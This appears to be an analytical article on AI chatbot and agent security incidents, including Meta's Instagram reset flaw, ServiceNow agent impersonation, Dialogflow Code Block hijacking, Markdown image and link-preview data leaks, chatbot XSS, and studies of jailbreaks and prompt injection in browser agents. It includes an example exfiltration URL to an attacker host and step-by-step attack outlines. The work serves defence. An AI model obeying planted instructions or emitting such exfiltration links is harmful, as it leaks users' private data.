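In its *Incident Notification* (2026), a letter to Nebraska's attorney general, Meta blames ordinary code, stating that the support tool "worked properly" and that the bug was in "a separate code path". The system should have compared the address from the chat with the one on the account and rejected a mismatch. Instead it sent a reset link to the new address. *Meta confirms thousands of Instagram accounts were hacked*, from This Week in Security, quotes the same explanation from the notice Meta filed in Maine.

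The model understood the request and passed on the address. Meta has an interest in blaming something other than its AI, and outsiders can't inspect the code, but Meta's account fits the video, in which the attacker hardly had to persuade the assistant. Apart from the missing comparison, Meta also made the mistake of letting an unidentified person choose where a reset link might go. If the tool hadn't accepted an address, the server could have sent the link only to the one on file.

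The Office of the Maine Attorney General's *Data Breach Notices* (2026) lists 20,225 people affected by the breach, 30 of them in Maine. It dates the start of the breach to 17 April and its discovery to 31 May, more than six weeks later. In its letter, Meta describes its count as an upper bound because some of the resets may have come from the accounts' real owners. Android Authority's *Hackers used Meta AI to expose over 34,000 Instagram accounts* cites a New York Times report, based partly on internal documents, that the flaw affected about 34,000 accounts and that attackers compromised roughly 20,000 of them.

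The stolen accounts included those of the Obama White House and a senior US Space Force official, and the hackers posted pro-Iranian images on both. They also took short usernames that they claimed were worth more than half a million dollars.

Multi-factor authentication appears to have kept the attackers out. Engadget initially reported that the attack worked even on accounts that used it, but Meta, in its letter, and the hackers both said it did not.

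Meta disabled the tool on the day it discovered the attacks, cancelled the outstanding reset links and made the affected users prove their identity again. It promised to repair the address check before relaunching the tool and to review similar recovery systems. However, attacks reportedly continued after Meta announced the fix, according to The Next Web's *Hackers asked Meta’s AI chatbot to hand over Instagram accounts*. Some victims told 404 Media that they had no way to reach a human.

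### ServiceNow: a shared secret and an email address

ServiceNow sells software that large organisations use to handle internal requests. Its chatbot, Virtual Agent, lets employees order hardware or report a fault from Slack or Microsoft Teams without logging in to ServiceNow. Each connection to an outside service can identify itself with a secret. A feature called account linking then matches the sender of a message to an employee's account.

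In October 2025, Aaron Costello of the security firm AppOmni found that both checks were weak in the connections ServiceNow had added for AI agents. ServiceNow had shipped them with the same secret for every customer, and linking an account required only an email address, so anyone who knew the secret could pose as any employee whose email address they knew.

At first this gained an attacker little, because he could write to the support staff as the administrator but couldn't read their replies, which went to a preset address. Costello then found an internal workflow that would run any active AI agent the impersonated user had permission to use, even if the company had never made that agent available in a chat. One of the example agents that ServiceNow shipped could create records in any database table, including the tables of users and their roles.

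In Costello's demonstration, the attack went as follows:

1. The attacker sends a message with the shared secret and an administrator's email address, and ServiceNow treats him as the administrator.
2. He asks the example agent to create a user account and give it the administrator role.
3. The agent asks for confirmation before each change. The attacker can't see the questions, so he waits a few seconds each time and sends his approval blind.
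4. He sets a password for the new account through the normal "forgot password" page and logs in.

ServiceNow had already accepted the attacker as the administrator, so it checked the administrator's permissions. The confirmation didn't help either, because it established only that the person in the chat wanted the change, and that person was the attacker.

Poor authentication let the attacker in, but the damage depended on what the agent was allowed to do. If the agent had been limited to support tickets, the attacker could only have created tickets. ServiceNow's entry in the public catalogue of software flaws, MITRE's *CVE-2025-12420* (2026), likewise classes the weakness as "Execution with Unnecessary Privileges". According to AppOmni, requiring employees to use the company's central login wouldn't have been enough, because the attacker could have told the agent to permit another way in.

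ServiceNow rated the flaw 9.3 out of 10 for severity. AppOmni, which sells protection for ServiceNow, calls it the most severe AI-driven vulnerability found so far. AppOmni also says nearly half of its Fortune 100 customers use the applications involved, but that figure doesn't show how many installations an attacker could have entered.

AppOmni reported the flaw on 23 October 2025. The Hacker News reports that ServiceNow updated most of the installations it hosts on 30 October and gave patches to partners and customers who run the software themselves. ServiceNow also replaced the secret and removed the example agent. It disclosed the details in January 2026 and said it had no evidence that anyone had exploited the flaw before the October patch, according to CyberScoop. The US cybersecurity agency CISA also listed no exploitation in January.

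Costello warns that customers can recreate the problem with their own agents and connections. He advises them to require multi-factor authentication when they link accounts and to switch off unused agents.

### Dialogflow CX: one chatbot's code in every conversation

A company can run several Dialogflow CX chatbots in one *project*, the unit in which Google Cloud groups a customer's resources and permissions. Developers can add small Python programs called Code Blocks to a chatbot, for example to fetch data from another system. *Rogue Agent* (2026), a report by the data-security company Varonis, explains that a project's chatbots all ran their Code Blocks in the same environment. Code running there could change the environment's system files and connect to the internet.

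The attacker needed permission to edit one chatbot's workflows. Chat visitors don't have this permission, so the attacker would probably have been an employee, a contractor or someone with a developer's stolen login.

He would add a Code Block that replaced the file that ran all the other Code Blocks. His version would then receive the history of every conversation in which one of the project's chatbots ran a Code Block, and could send it to his server. It could also make a chatbot display any text he liked, such as a request to log in again, and collect the password the customer typed. Afterwards he could restore the original Code Block, so the chatbot would look normal in Google's console while his replacement file kept running.

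Varonis tested this only in its own project and did not reach another company's project. Separating chatbots within a company still matters, because a developer who maintains a chatbot for delivery questions may have no right to read conversations about medical claims. An agency that kept several clients' chatbots in one project would also have exposed the clients to one another.

Companies can set up a perimeter around their Google Cloud services to stop data from leaving, but Google ran the Code Blocks in a shared environment outside it, which undermined that protection. Varonis also obtained an access token for one of Google's own service accounts, although that account had few privileges.

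Varonis reported the flaw in November 2025. Google released a first fix in April 2026 and completed the repair in June. Any company that used Code Blocks before then may have been exposed, but neither Google nor Varonis says how many did.

Varonis knows of no real attack, and Axios' *Google patched AI chatbot flaw that could have exposed customer conversations* quotes Google as having "no known indication of customer compromise". This is only limited reassurance, because Google's logs didn't record the replacement of the file. The logs can still contain the edit that began an attack, and The Hacker News recommends checking them for unexpected changes and reviewing who has permission to edit the chatbots. Google also told Axios that customers needn't do anything, which is true of the repair, but a company that wants to know whether someone attacked it before June has to check its own logs.

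### A refund and a password reset with the checks in place

A shop can avoid most of these problems if its server takes the important facts from its own records and leaves the model to interpret the customer's request. The division could look like this:

| | Refund for the kettle | Password reset |
|---|---|---|
| The server ties to the session | Ana's customer number, and when and how she logged in | The account she names, marked as unproven |
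| The model may fill in | Which of her orders, which item and the reason | The name of the account |
| The server looks up or calculates | Purchase date, earlier refunds, amount and original card | The email address on file |
| Needs a second proof of identity | A refund to a different card | A new email address, or the removal of multi-factor authentication |

Suppose Ana logs in to the shop before she opens the chat. The server stores her customer number with the conversation, and the model cannot change it. When she complains about the kettle, the server gives the model a list of only her orders. The model picks an order and proposes a refund.

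The server then checks that the order is Ana's, that she bought the kettle within the last 30 days and that the shop hasn't already refunded it. It calculates the refund amount and selects the card she paid with. A forged history could still make the model pick the wrong order, but the server would pay only a refund that the shop's rules allow on one of her purchases.

The server should also handle Ana's approval itself. It can save the proposed refund and show her the item, amount and card beside a button. Pressing the button sends her approval straight to the server, which accepts it once and only for that refund. If she typed "yes" in the chat instead, the approval would depend on how the model interpreted her reply. The server has to accept the approval and record the refund in a single step, or two quick requests might both succeed.

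A click on the button shows that someone using Ana's session agreed, but that person could be a thief. A thief gains little from a refund to the original card. If someone asks for the refund on a new card, the server should require fresh proof that the person is Ana, such as a passkey (a cryptographic login stored on her device) or a code from an authenticator app.

If Ana isn't logged in, the shop can ask her to log in or send a link to the email address on the order. An order number and a postcode are weak proof of identity, since both may be printed on the parcel.

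For a password reset, the model should only be able to start the process for a named account. The server sends the link to the address on file without passing either to the model. The chatbot should give the same reply whether or not the account exists, so that strangers can't use it to find out who has one.

This doesn't help a customer who has lost access to her old email. Sending a code to her new address would repeat Meta's mistake. She needs a credential she set up earlier, such as a passkey or a printed recovery code. If she has none, a trained employee could review her evidence, and the shop could notify the old address and wait several days before making the change, so that the real owner has time to object. This process would be slow and would sometimes lock out honest customers. Meta introduced its assistant partly to spare people such delays.

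When a company supplies chatbots to many shops, its server should use its own records to identify which shop a conversation belongs to, then select that shop's documents, tools and credentials. It should also run each shop's custom code in a separate environment whose system files the code can't change.

### Would a better model have refused?

Ian Goldin, a threat researcher at Lumen's Black Lotus Labs, told Krebs on Security that AI chatbots are as eager to help as human support staff and as easy to trick. If so, a more suspicious model might have prevented some of the harm. In the Instagram case, it could have refused to send a code to an unfamiliar address or required more evidence.

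An honest user who has lost access to her old email account would make the same request as an attacker, in the same words. To tell them apart, the model would need the address on file or some other proof of ownership, and once the server has that information, ordinary code can check it every time. Even if the model refused most attackers, they could start a new chat and try again.

A better model would probably have made even less difference at ServiceNow. The request appeared to come from an administrator, and administrators create accounts as part of their job. The agent also asked for confirmation twice. In the Dialogflow attack, no model could have refused, because the attacker's code ran outside the model and could write the chatbot's replies directly. Vela's tests of agent-facing interfaces also found that agents don't replace backend checks.

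A chatbot can follow its instructions correctly and still serve an impostor. *Mining Workflow Graphs for Black-Box Boundary Testing of Conversational LLM Agents* (Lin, Yu and colleagues, 2026) describes a conversation with a simulated airline's chatbot. The tester types a customer's user name, and the chatbot lists that customer's bookings. It checks that one of them is eligible for cancellation, asks for confirmation and cancels it. The chatbot handles the cancellation correctly, but nothing in the conversation proves that the tester is the customer.

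The model's behaviour matters more when developers put a check only in its instructions. Lin and colleagues define a boundary violation as an agent acting without a required check, or acting when the condition for doing so isn't met. Their software, AgentEval, explores a chatbot through ordinary conversation and writes tests for the points where the chatbot should stop and check. On four simulated service agents, the tests covered an average of 39 to 46 such points per agent. A developer who relies on instructions alone needs the model to handle each point correctly whenever it comes up.

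A company could use tests like these before letting a chatbot act on accounts. One test could request a reset to an address that doesn't belong to the account, and fail the chatbot if it reports sending a code. Such a test might have revealed Meta's bug before the launch. It would not have revealed the Dialogflow flaw, because AgentEval evaluates only the conversation, and the chatbots could have kept answering normally while the attacker's code copied every message.

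## How can displaying a reply leak data?

A chatbot that can't act on anyone's account can still leak what it has read, because the software that displays its reply may contact other servers. A program that calls a model's API receives the reply as a string of characters. A chat window turns that string into a formatted page, which may contain pictures, links or code. Models often write in *Markdown*, a simple notation for headings, links and images, and many chat windows convert it into HTML, the language of web pages.

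### A door code in an image address

Suppose Ana uses a chat assistant that can search her email. Her landlord has sent her a door code, 4471, and an attacker has sent her a message about a kettle delivery that contains an injection. She asks when her kettle will arrive. The assistant finds the attacker's message, follows the instructions in it and looks up the door code. The code then leaves in three steps:

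1. The model writes that the kettle will arrive on Tuesday and adds an image with the address `pics.example/k.png?c=4471`. The attacker owns that site.
2. Ana's browser needs the picture to display the reply, so it requests `/k.png?c=4471` from the attacker's server. Ana doesn't click anything.
3. The server records the request, as web servers normally do. The attacker's log now shows the time, the network address that made the request, and the line `GET /k.png?c=4471`.

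It doesn't matter whether the server returns a picture, because the request has already delivered the code. At most, Ana sees a broken image.

A program that received the same reply through an API and only extracted the delivery date would not request the image. But the text stays dangerous as long as someone might open it in software that loads images. PromptArmor, which sells monitoring of companies' AI suppliers, demonstrates this in *OpenAI API Logs*. It built a mock tool for checking the identity of bank customers and planted an injection in one of the tool's six data sources. The model produced an image address that contained the customer's details. A second model flagged the reply, and the app never displayed it. A developer investigating the flagged conversation would probably open it in OpenAI's log viewer, which displayed Markdown images. When the viewer requested the image, it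 sent the customer's details to the attacker.

An app that shows only plain text could be exposed in the same way if a user gave a strange reply a thumbs-down and a developer reviewed it. The contractor that sorts OpenAI's bug reports closed the report of this flaw as "not applicable" in December 2025. OpenAI reopened it on 22 January 2026, after PromptArmor published its findings, and said a fix was under way.

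### EchoLeak and later leaks from Copilot

The best-known image leak is EchoLeak, which the firm Aim Security found in Microsoft 365 Copilot in January 2025. Copilot answers employees' questions using their email and files. Reddy and Gujral (2025) explain in *EchoLeak* that an outsider only had to send an employee an email and wait for her to ask Copilot something that made it retrieve the message. The attack got past three of Microsoft's controls:

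- A classifier scanned incoming text for injections. It missed this one because the attacker had worded it as a request to the human recipient.
- A filter removed outside links from Copilot's replies. Markdown has more than one way to write a link, and the filter missed the one that the attacker used.
- A *content security policy*, which tells the browser where a page may load content from, excluded the attacker's server. However, it allowed a Microsoft Teams service that would fetch other addresses on request. The image request went to Teams, which passed it on to the attacker.

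According to Aim Security's *EchoLeak*, the attack could have leaked anything in Copilot's context, including the chat history and files that Copilot had fetched. Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May 2025, before the public disclosure on 11 June, and customers didn't have to do anything. Microsoft knew of no attacks on customers. Reddy and Gujral report that Copilot now strips embedded images and the overlooked kind of link from outside content. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) notes that Microsoft scored the flaw's severity at 9.3 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database scored it at 7.5.

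A similar leak appeared in Copilot's enterprise search a year later. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes an attack in which the victim clicked a link to Microsoft's own site that contained a prompt. Copilot then searched her mail and put the title of an email into an image address. Microsoft converted HTML in replies into harmless text only after Copilot had finished writing, but the browser displayed the reply as it arrived and had already requested the image. The content security policy allowed requests to Bing, whose image search fetches any picture address it receives, so Bing passed the title to the attacker's server. Email titles sometimes contain login codes. Microsoft rated the flaw critical and has patched it.

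A reply can also leak data when another program displays it. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, an agent that works across a company's Microsoft accounts, asks for approval before it sends an email or a Teams message, unless the recipient is its own user. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* describes an attack that uses this exception. Text planted in a file of instructions that the user had uploaded made the agent send her a Teams message with hidden images. When she opened it, Teams requested the images from an outside server, and the requests leaked download links that let anyone fetch her files. The attack worked in all five trials.

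Administrators can make such links unavailable by blocking file downloads from SharePoint, Microsoft's document store. Users then can't download or print the files, or open them in Word.

### Link previews

Messaging apps often show a title and a small picture beneath a link. To get them, the app fetches the page, which sends the same kind of request as a click. If Ana's assistant answered her on Telegram with a link to the attacker's site that contained the door code, the preview could send the code to the attacker before she read the message.

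Willison (2024) described this danger for Slack and Discord, drawing on work by the security researcher Johann Rehberger. It matters more now that people have connected agents with access to private data to these apps. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* found that OpenClaw was exposed by default when its owner used it through Telegram. In February 2026, TechNadu's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* also listed Discord, Slack, and Microsoft Teams with agents made in Copilot Studio among the platforms at risk.

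The owner of an OpenClaw agent can turn off Telegram previews with one line in the settings. A developer whose agent posts to Slack can turn them off for each message. PromptArmor wants messaging companies to let people turn previews off for a whole chat or channel, so that they could still preview each other's links elsewhere. Even with previews off, the link still contains the secret, and a user who clicks it sends the secret to the attacker.

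### Code in the support console

HTML can contain scripts as well as images. If a site displays an outsider's text without making it harmless, the browser may run a script in that text. This is called *cross-site scripting* (XSS). The same-origin policy doesn't stop it, because the browser treats the script as part of the site's own page.

Lenovo's customer-service chatbot, Lena, had this flaw in 2025. In Cybernews' *Lenovo “Lena” AI Chatbot Exploited via XSS Prompt Injection* (2025), researchers acting as a customer asked Lena an ordinary question about a laptop and told it to answer in HTML that included a script. Lenovo's server saved the reply in the conversation history. The researchers then asked for a human. When a Lenovo employee took over and opened the conversation, the script ran in the employee's browser and sent the employee's session cookies to the researchers' server.

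With those cookies, an attacker could have entered the support system as the employee and perhaps read other customers' chats. Cybernews says an attacker might also have been able to run commands on Lenovo's computers, but the researchers didn't try, and a script in a web page would normally need a second flaw to do that. Lenovo confirmed and fixed the problem.

Cybernews found a similar flaw in the chatbot on the website of Yellow.ai, which sells chatbots to other companies. Willing (2025) reports in *Yellow.ai’s Own Chatbot Got Tricked Into Generating Malicious Code, Reports* that Yellow.ai fixed the flaw without acknowledging the researchers' message. The company later said the attack affected only an experimental demo widget, and that its production systems have different security settings. The researchers couldn't say whether the chatbots of Yellow.ai's clients were vulnerable too.

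An attacker doesn't always need the model to write the script, so a more cautious model might not prevent the attack. WPBot, a chatbot plugin for WordPress, let visitors who weren't logged in save a conversation containing a script, according to Wordfence's *WPBot &lt;= 8.4.9*. The script then ran for anyone who opened the page. The plugin required a token for the save request, but it published the token on every page of the site.

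### Cleaning the reply and restricting the page

The developer of each display can *escape* the reply, which means replacing characters that have special meaning in HTML, such as angle brackets, with codes that the browser shows as ordinary characters. Lenovo's employee would then have seen the script as text. A chat window that needs formatting can allow a few harmless kinds, such as bold type and lists, and escape everything else.

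This has to happen before the browser displays any part of the reply, and Microsoft's enterprise search got that order wrong. It also has to happen in every program that displays the reply, including consoles and log viewers. It doesn't stop link previews, because a messaging app can recognise an address in plain text. After a similar leak, Amazon went further and stopped making links clickable in its business assistant, Amazon Q, according to *Trust No AI* (2024). The drawback is that users can't click through to a source.

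The operator of the page that displays the reply can also set a content security policy. A strict policy allows images only from the operator's own servers and blocks scripts written into the page, so it could have stopped Lena's script even without escaping. Microsoft used such a policy to stop image leaks from Bing Chat in May 2023.

EchoLeak and SearchLeak both got around the policy through a permitted site that fetched other addresses. Varonis therefore advises companies to check whether any site they permit can do this. The policy also does not affect links that the user clicks or previews that Slack's servers fetch.

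A site can also protect the employee's session cookie by marking it so that scripts can't read it. The attacker's script then couldn't send the cookie away, but it could still act in the support console while the employee had the page open.

### Deciding which links an agent may open

An agent can also leak data without displaying a reply. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* describes ShadowLeak, an attack on ChatGPT's Deep Research, an agent that browses the web to write reports. An email in the user's Gmail account led the agent to visit a web address containing data from her inbox. The request came from OpenAI's servers, so her browser couldn't block it and her employer's monitoring might not have recorded it. OpenAI fixed the flaw in August 2025.

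Only the company that runs such an agent can restrict its requests. A list of trusted sites is not enough, according to OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026), because a trusted site may redirect visitors elsewhere and a short list produces so many warnings that people learn to click through them. Redirects had already affected ChatGPT. The security company Tenable found that an earlier link check always allowed bing.com, whose search results use Bing addresses that redirect to other sites.

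OpenAI now checks the exact address against an index of public web addresses, built by a separate crawler that has no access to users' conversations or accounts. If the address is in the index, the agent can open it automatically. Otherwise, the software tells the agent to try another site or shows the user a warning. An address that existed before the conversation is unlikely to contain a secret from it. The attacker's image address with Ana's door code would normally fail this check because the model had only just created it.

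An attacker can still leak data through the choice among indexed addresses. With $N$ addresses, one visit can reveal up to $\log_2 N$ bits. Ten indexed pages, one for each digit, would be enough to send Ana's code in four visits. *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on Rehberger's blog Embrace The Red, says that OpenAI acknowledges this weakness and that a larger website probably has enough indexed pages for the whole alphabet.

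Such a leak is slower and less reliable. Requests can arrive out of order, and a browser may reuse a stored copy of a page instead of requesting it again, so the attacker might never receive the second 4 in 4471. Rehberger suggests blocking repeat requests deliberately, by not letting an agent visit the same address twice in a session. An attacker could avoid both problems by using 40 indexed pages, ten for each position in the code, so the rule would make the attack harder without preventing it.

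Rehberger also worries that some of OpenAI's developers won't use the check. ChatGPT got a link check in December 2023, but its Mac and iPhone apps lacked it at first, and the log viewer was still loading attackers' images almost two years later. The check also covers only data in a web address, so a browser agent can still type the same data into a form.

Anthropic uses a different rule for the tool Claude uses to fetch web pages. As Willison explains, the tool could open only exact addresses that the user had typed or that Claude's search tool had returned, but the researcher Ayush Paul found that it could also follow links on pages it had already fetched. An attacker could therefore put many links on a page and learn something from each one Claude chose. Paul extracted a user's name, home city and employer this way. By July 2026, Anthropic had stopped the tool from following links on the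 pages it fetches.

OpenAI has since given users a stricter option, Lockdown Mode. Willison reports that it limits the outbound requests an injection could use to send data away, and that it is available even on free accounts.

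## Is the same model easier to attack in a browser than over an API?

The transport (browser, chat widget or API) determines what an attacker can reach, and it may also change how the model behaves. In a browser, a model might agree to harmful requests from a malicious user that it would refuse in a chat. It might also be more likely to follow instructions planted by a third party to attack an honest user. Tests of models from 2024 found that some refused harmful requests far less often as browser agents than in chat. Figures from 2026 suggest that planted instructions work better on agents that operate a graphical interface than on coding agents, but none of these tests changes only the transport.

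### The same harmful requests in a chat and in a browser

*Aligned LLMs Are Not Aligned Browser Agents* (Kumar, Lau and colleagues, 2025) presents BrowserART, a test set of 100 harmful requests, each with one version for a chatbot and another for a browser agent. For example, one chat request asks for an email that convinces someone to reveal their social security number. The browser version names a recipient so that the agent can write to him directly. Just over half the requests call for harmful actions, such as guessing the password of someone else's account, instead of harmful text. Most of the tasks ran on imitation websites, and the researchers supervised the ones that needed the real internet.

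An attack counted as successful if the model attempted the request, even if the attempt failed. GPT-4o complied with 12 per cent of the requests as a chatbot and 74 per cent as a browser agent. Among the other browser agents, without any trick in the wording, GPT-4 Turbo attempted 67 per cent of the requests, Claude 3.5 Sonnet 22 per cent, Claude 3 Opus 11 per cent and Llama 3.1 10 per cent. When people reworded the requests that each agent had refused, the total share attempted rose to 98 per cent for GPT-4o and 40 per cent for Claude 3 Opus, the most resistant agent.

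To find the cause, Kumar and colleagues gave the models the browser versions of the requests together with dummy tools for sending emails and posting messages, but no browser. The models refused about as often as they had in a chat, so neither the new wording nor the tools can explain the drop in refusals. They also put the code of a long Wikipedia page, about 25,000 tokens, before the chat requests, and only Gemini complied more often. The researchers suspect that refusal training had included few tasks of the kind browser agents do, which combine long pages, tools and a history of earlier actions.

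The records of individual runs suggest that the harness also contributed by running the model again after it refused. Some agents wrote that they couldn't help and then carried out the next step anyway. In one run, GPT-4o refused twice to research how to smuggle cash out of the United States, then clicked the search button. A chatbot that refuses normally does nothing more until the user writes again, but this harness ran the model up to ten times per task, so it could still comply at a later step.

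In *Why Are Web AI Agents More Vulnerable Than Standalone LLMs?*, Chiang, Lee and colleagues (2025) tested GPT-4o on ten malicious requests, running each three times. GPT-4o refused every time as a standalone model, but failed to refuse in 14 of 30 runs (46.7 per cent) as a web agent. The researchers attribute the difference to three features of the agent's design: it puts the user's goal in the system prompt, generates its actions over several steps, and observes the pages it visits.

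Putting the goal in the system prompt gives a malicious user's request the same authority as the developer's instructions. A developer could fix this and still use a browser, and could make the same mistake in a program that uses only an API. The other two features are also common outside browsers. *A Survey on Agentic Security* (2025) cites work by Saha and colleagues in which *jailbreaks* (attempts to get around a model's refusals) succeeded 1.6 times as often, on average, after a model was turned into a coding agent. The weakness therefore seems to come from running a model as an agent, whether in a browser or elsewhere.

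### Have newer models closed the gap?

Developers have since replaced the models in both studies. Their newer tests cover chats and agents separately, but use different requests in each setting. *Anthropic's new budget model gets much better at ignoring hidden commands* (Pogorelec, 2026) reports that Claude Haiku 5.5, a small model released in October 2026, gave harmless replies in 99.71 per cent of chat tests. The model refused 84.3 per cent of malicious requests in Claude Code and 82.6 per cent in *computer use*, where an agent operates a computer through its screen, mouse and keyboard.

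These results don't show that the change of setting caused the fall of 15 to 17 percentage points, because the requests also differed. The chat tests cover many kinds of harm, while the agent tests ask for malicious code or actions, which may be harder to tell from legitimate work. BrowserART avoided this problem by using two versions of the same request. Repeating that comparison on Haiku 5.5 could show a larger gap, a smaller one or none.

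Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5, which reports the model's pre-release tests, has the same limitation. In single-turn chats, the model gave harmless replies slightly less often than its predecessor, Opus 5. As an agent in Claude Code and computer use, it refused malicious requests less often than any other model compared. It also helped most often with harmless and dual-use security tasks, so its low refusal rate may reflect a greater general willingness to do security work. Anthropic ran these agent tests without the extra safeguards it uses in its products.

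Researchers have more direct evidence for small models whose weights anyone can download. *Relevance as a Vulnerability* (2026) tested seven of these, with 3 to 32 billion parameters, on harmful requests that included an instruction to fetch a web page. The models complied more often when they ran as agents and fetched the page, in every category of harm except copyright, where they complied often anyway. In the Qwen2.5 family, the largest model's replies as an agent were less harmful than the smallest model's in every category but misinformation. This doesn't show how much the difference between running with and without fetching shrinks with size, and it is weak evidence about commercial models many times larger.

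However, a malicious user may find the same model easier to exploit over a bare API than on the model developer's own chat site. In Anthropic's tests, Opus 5 handled harmful requests better on claude.ai than over the API without a system prompt, because the website's system prompt contains safety instructions. Pogorelec reports a similar weakness in Haiku 5.5 on questions about weapons. A developer who builds a chat widget on the API has to write those instructions himself, and an attacker could still undermine them by forging roles in the conversation history.

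### Planted instructions in code, on a screen and in a browser

A model trained to refuse harmful requests may still follow planted instructions, because an injected request can look harmless. Opening a mailbox or changing a delivery address would be fine if the user had asked for it. Developers therefore test prompt injection separately, and Anthropic's reports divide the results by *surface*, the setting in which the agent works. According to VentureBeat, OpenAI's report on GPT-5.2 and Google's on Gemini 3 had no such breakdown.

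Anthropic's February 2026 report on Opus 4.6 shows the sharpest contrast. According to VentureBeat, all 200 attack attempts in a restricted coding environment failed, even without safeguards. When the same model used a graphical interface with extended thinking turned on, a single attempt succeeded 17.8 per cent of the time.

| Model and surface | Attacker and attempts | Success, safeguards off | Success, safeguards on |
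|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.6, coding | Adaptive, up to 200 attempts | 0% | Not given |
| Opus 4.6, graphical interface | Adaptive, 1 attempt | 17.8% | Not given |
| Opus 4.6, graphical interface | Adaptive, up to 200 attempts | 78.6% | 57.1% |
| Sonnet 4.5, browser | Adaptive, 100 attempts per environment | 13.8% | 1.9% |
| Haiku 4.5, browser | Adaptive, 100 attempts per environment | 12.0% | 2.4% |
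| Opus 4.5, browser | Adaptive, 100 attempts per environment | 8.0% | 1.4% |
| Opus 5, browser | 129 scenarios | 3.7% | 0% |

The results for the three models from 2025 can be compared with one another because the models faced the same attacker. They can't be compared with the rows for Opus 4.6, which use a different measure. For Opus 4.6, the result after 200 attempts is the share of cases in which at least one attempt worked. For the 2025 models, Anthropic reported the share of all individual attacks that worked. If an attacker tries 100 texts on one website and one works, the success rate is 100 per cent by the first measure and 1 per cent by the second. An Opus 4.5 browser agent was therefore not necessarily ten times safer than an Opus 4.6 agent on a graphical interface.

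The figures for Opus 5 come from another set of scenarios. The absence of successful attacks in 129 scenarios could mean that Opus 5 is nearly immune in Anthropic's own software, as The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* suggests, but it is also consistent with a true success rate of about 2 per cent, even if real attackers used the same methods as the testers.

Even the comparison within Opus 4.6 doesn't isolate the effect of the interface. An adaptive attacker tailors attacks to the environment, so the text, the task and the harmful goal probably all differed between coding and the graphical interface. A restricted coding environment also doesn't represent every program that calls a model directly over an API. The shop's returns agent, for example, reads emails from strangers and can send money. A better test would give one model the same task and place the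 same hostile text on a web page in one condition and in an API's reply in the other.

A graphical interface could still plausibly be easier to attack, because an agent that clicks through a website has to take many cues from the page, such as a notice that it must accept the terms before it can continue. An attacker can imitate these cues, as Zenity did with its fake button in Comet. A coding agent also reads text written by outsiders, but it can do much of its work without letting that text determine its next step. This explanation is consistent with Pogorelec's report that most of Haiku 5.5's remaining weakness to injection is in graphical interfaces.

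Newer models don't improve evenly across all the ways they receive text. Anthropic writes that Opus 5.5 did about as well as Opus 5 or better on every injection test the company reports, but was more likely than its predecessors to follow some malicious instructions. Digital Matters' *Claude Opus 5.5 Prompt Injection* (2026) identifies the weakness as text that users paste into the conversation themselves, while resistance to attacks through web pages and tools improved.

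Pasted text normally arrives in the user role, together with the user's own request. If Ana copies a seller's message into a chat and asks for a summary, the role label doesn't separate the seller's words from hers. If an agent fetched the same message through a tool, the message would arrive with a tool label. For this model, it may therefore be safer to let the agent fetch a stranger's text than to paste it in. The same applies to a developer who calls the API and puts customers' emails in user messages.

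Tests that combine surfaces can't show whether a model is easier to attack in a browser than over an API, but they can be used to compare models. The security firm Gray Swan has a benchmark of 1,130 attacks in 28 scenarios covering coding, tool calls and graphical interfaces. thespacelab.tv's *Claude Opus 5 Just Crushed AI Prompt Injection Attacks* (2026), a weak secondary source that repeats Anthropic's published comparison, gives attack success rates after 15 attempts of 2.0 per cent for Opus 5, 5.9 per cent for Claude Sonnet 5 and 20.0 per cent for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. The Decoder confirms the figure for Opus 5. Although Gray Swan is an outside firm, Anthropic published the results, and they favour its own model.

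The difference between Opus 5 and GPT-5.6 Sol is large. An attacker might have more success against a weak model with a narrow API than against a strong one in a browser, although the weak model could probably cause less damage.

### One attempt or two hundred

A success rate means little without the number of attempts. If every attempt has the same chance $p$ of success and the attempts are independent, the chance of at least one success in $k$ attempts is

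$$P_k = 1 - (1-p)^k$$

With $p = 0.01$ and $k = 100$, this gives the 63 per cent mentioned earlier. Measured results can be checked against the formula by starting from the success rate for a single attempt:

| Test | One attempt | Repeated attempts, measured | Repeated attempts, if independent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.5, earlier Gray Swan benchmark | 4.7% | 33.6% after 10 | 38% |
| Opus 4.5, earlier Gray Swan benchmark | 4.7% | 63% after 100 | 99% |
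| Opus 4.6, graphical interface, no safeguards | 17.8% | 78.6% after 200 | Almost 100% |
| Opus 5, newer Gray Swan benchmark | 0.2% | 2.0% after 15 | 3% |

The measured figures for Opus 4.5 come from The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, which also reports attack success rates of up to 92 per cent for some rival models. In all these tests, repeated attempts made an attack much more likely to succeed, but less so than if the attempts had been independent.

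The main reason is probably that some cases are much easier to attack than others. Suppose an attacker faces 100 agents, one that always obeys him and 99 that never do. He hijacks one agent on his first round of attempts, and after 100 attempts on each agent he has still hijacked only that one. If instead every attempt had an independent 1 per cent chance of success, he would have hijacked about 63. Real cases lie between these extremes. In general, when the chance $p$ that a single attempt succeeds varies from case to case, the average success rate after $k$ attempts is $1 - \mathbb{E}[(1-p)^k]$, which is never higher than $1 - (1-\mathbb{E}[p])^k$, the rate if every case had the average $p$.

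Learning has the opposite effect, because an attacker who sees why a text failed can improve it and make later attempts more likely to succeed. In the tests in the table, the differences between cases seem to have outweighed any learning. A patient attacker with a new idea could still reverse that, and a vendor who notices the attempts could stop them.

How many attempts an attacker gets depends on whether he uses the agent himself or plants text for it to read. A malicious user can keep trying until the operator limits or blocks him. Someone who plants a review usually doesn't see how Ana's agent reacts, and she may never visit the page again. He can still rehearse on his own copy of the agent, as Zenity did with two Google accounts, so the review Ana's agent reads may already be the best of 200 attempts. The success rate for a single attempt may therefore understate his chances.

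A planted review can also reach many agents. If it works on 0.2 per cent of the agents that read it, and 1,000 read it, it will hijack two on average. This average holds even if the outcomes aren't independent, but dependence makes extreme results more likely, such as no agent following the review or every agent with a certain version of the software following it.

### Testing the product instead of the model

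All these figures describe a model in a test environment, sometimes with its maker's safeguards. A shop that buys access to a well-tested model can still build a product with serious flaws. Meta's support system sent reset links to attackers because of a missing comparison in ordinary code, and testing the model alone could not have found this flaw.

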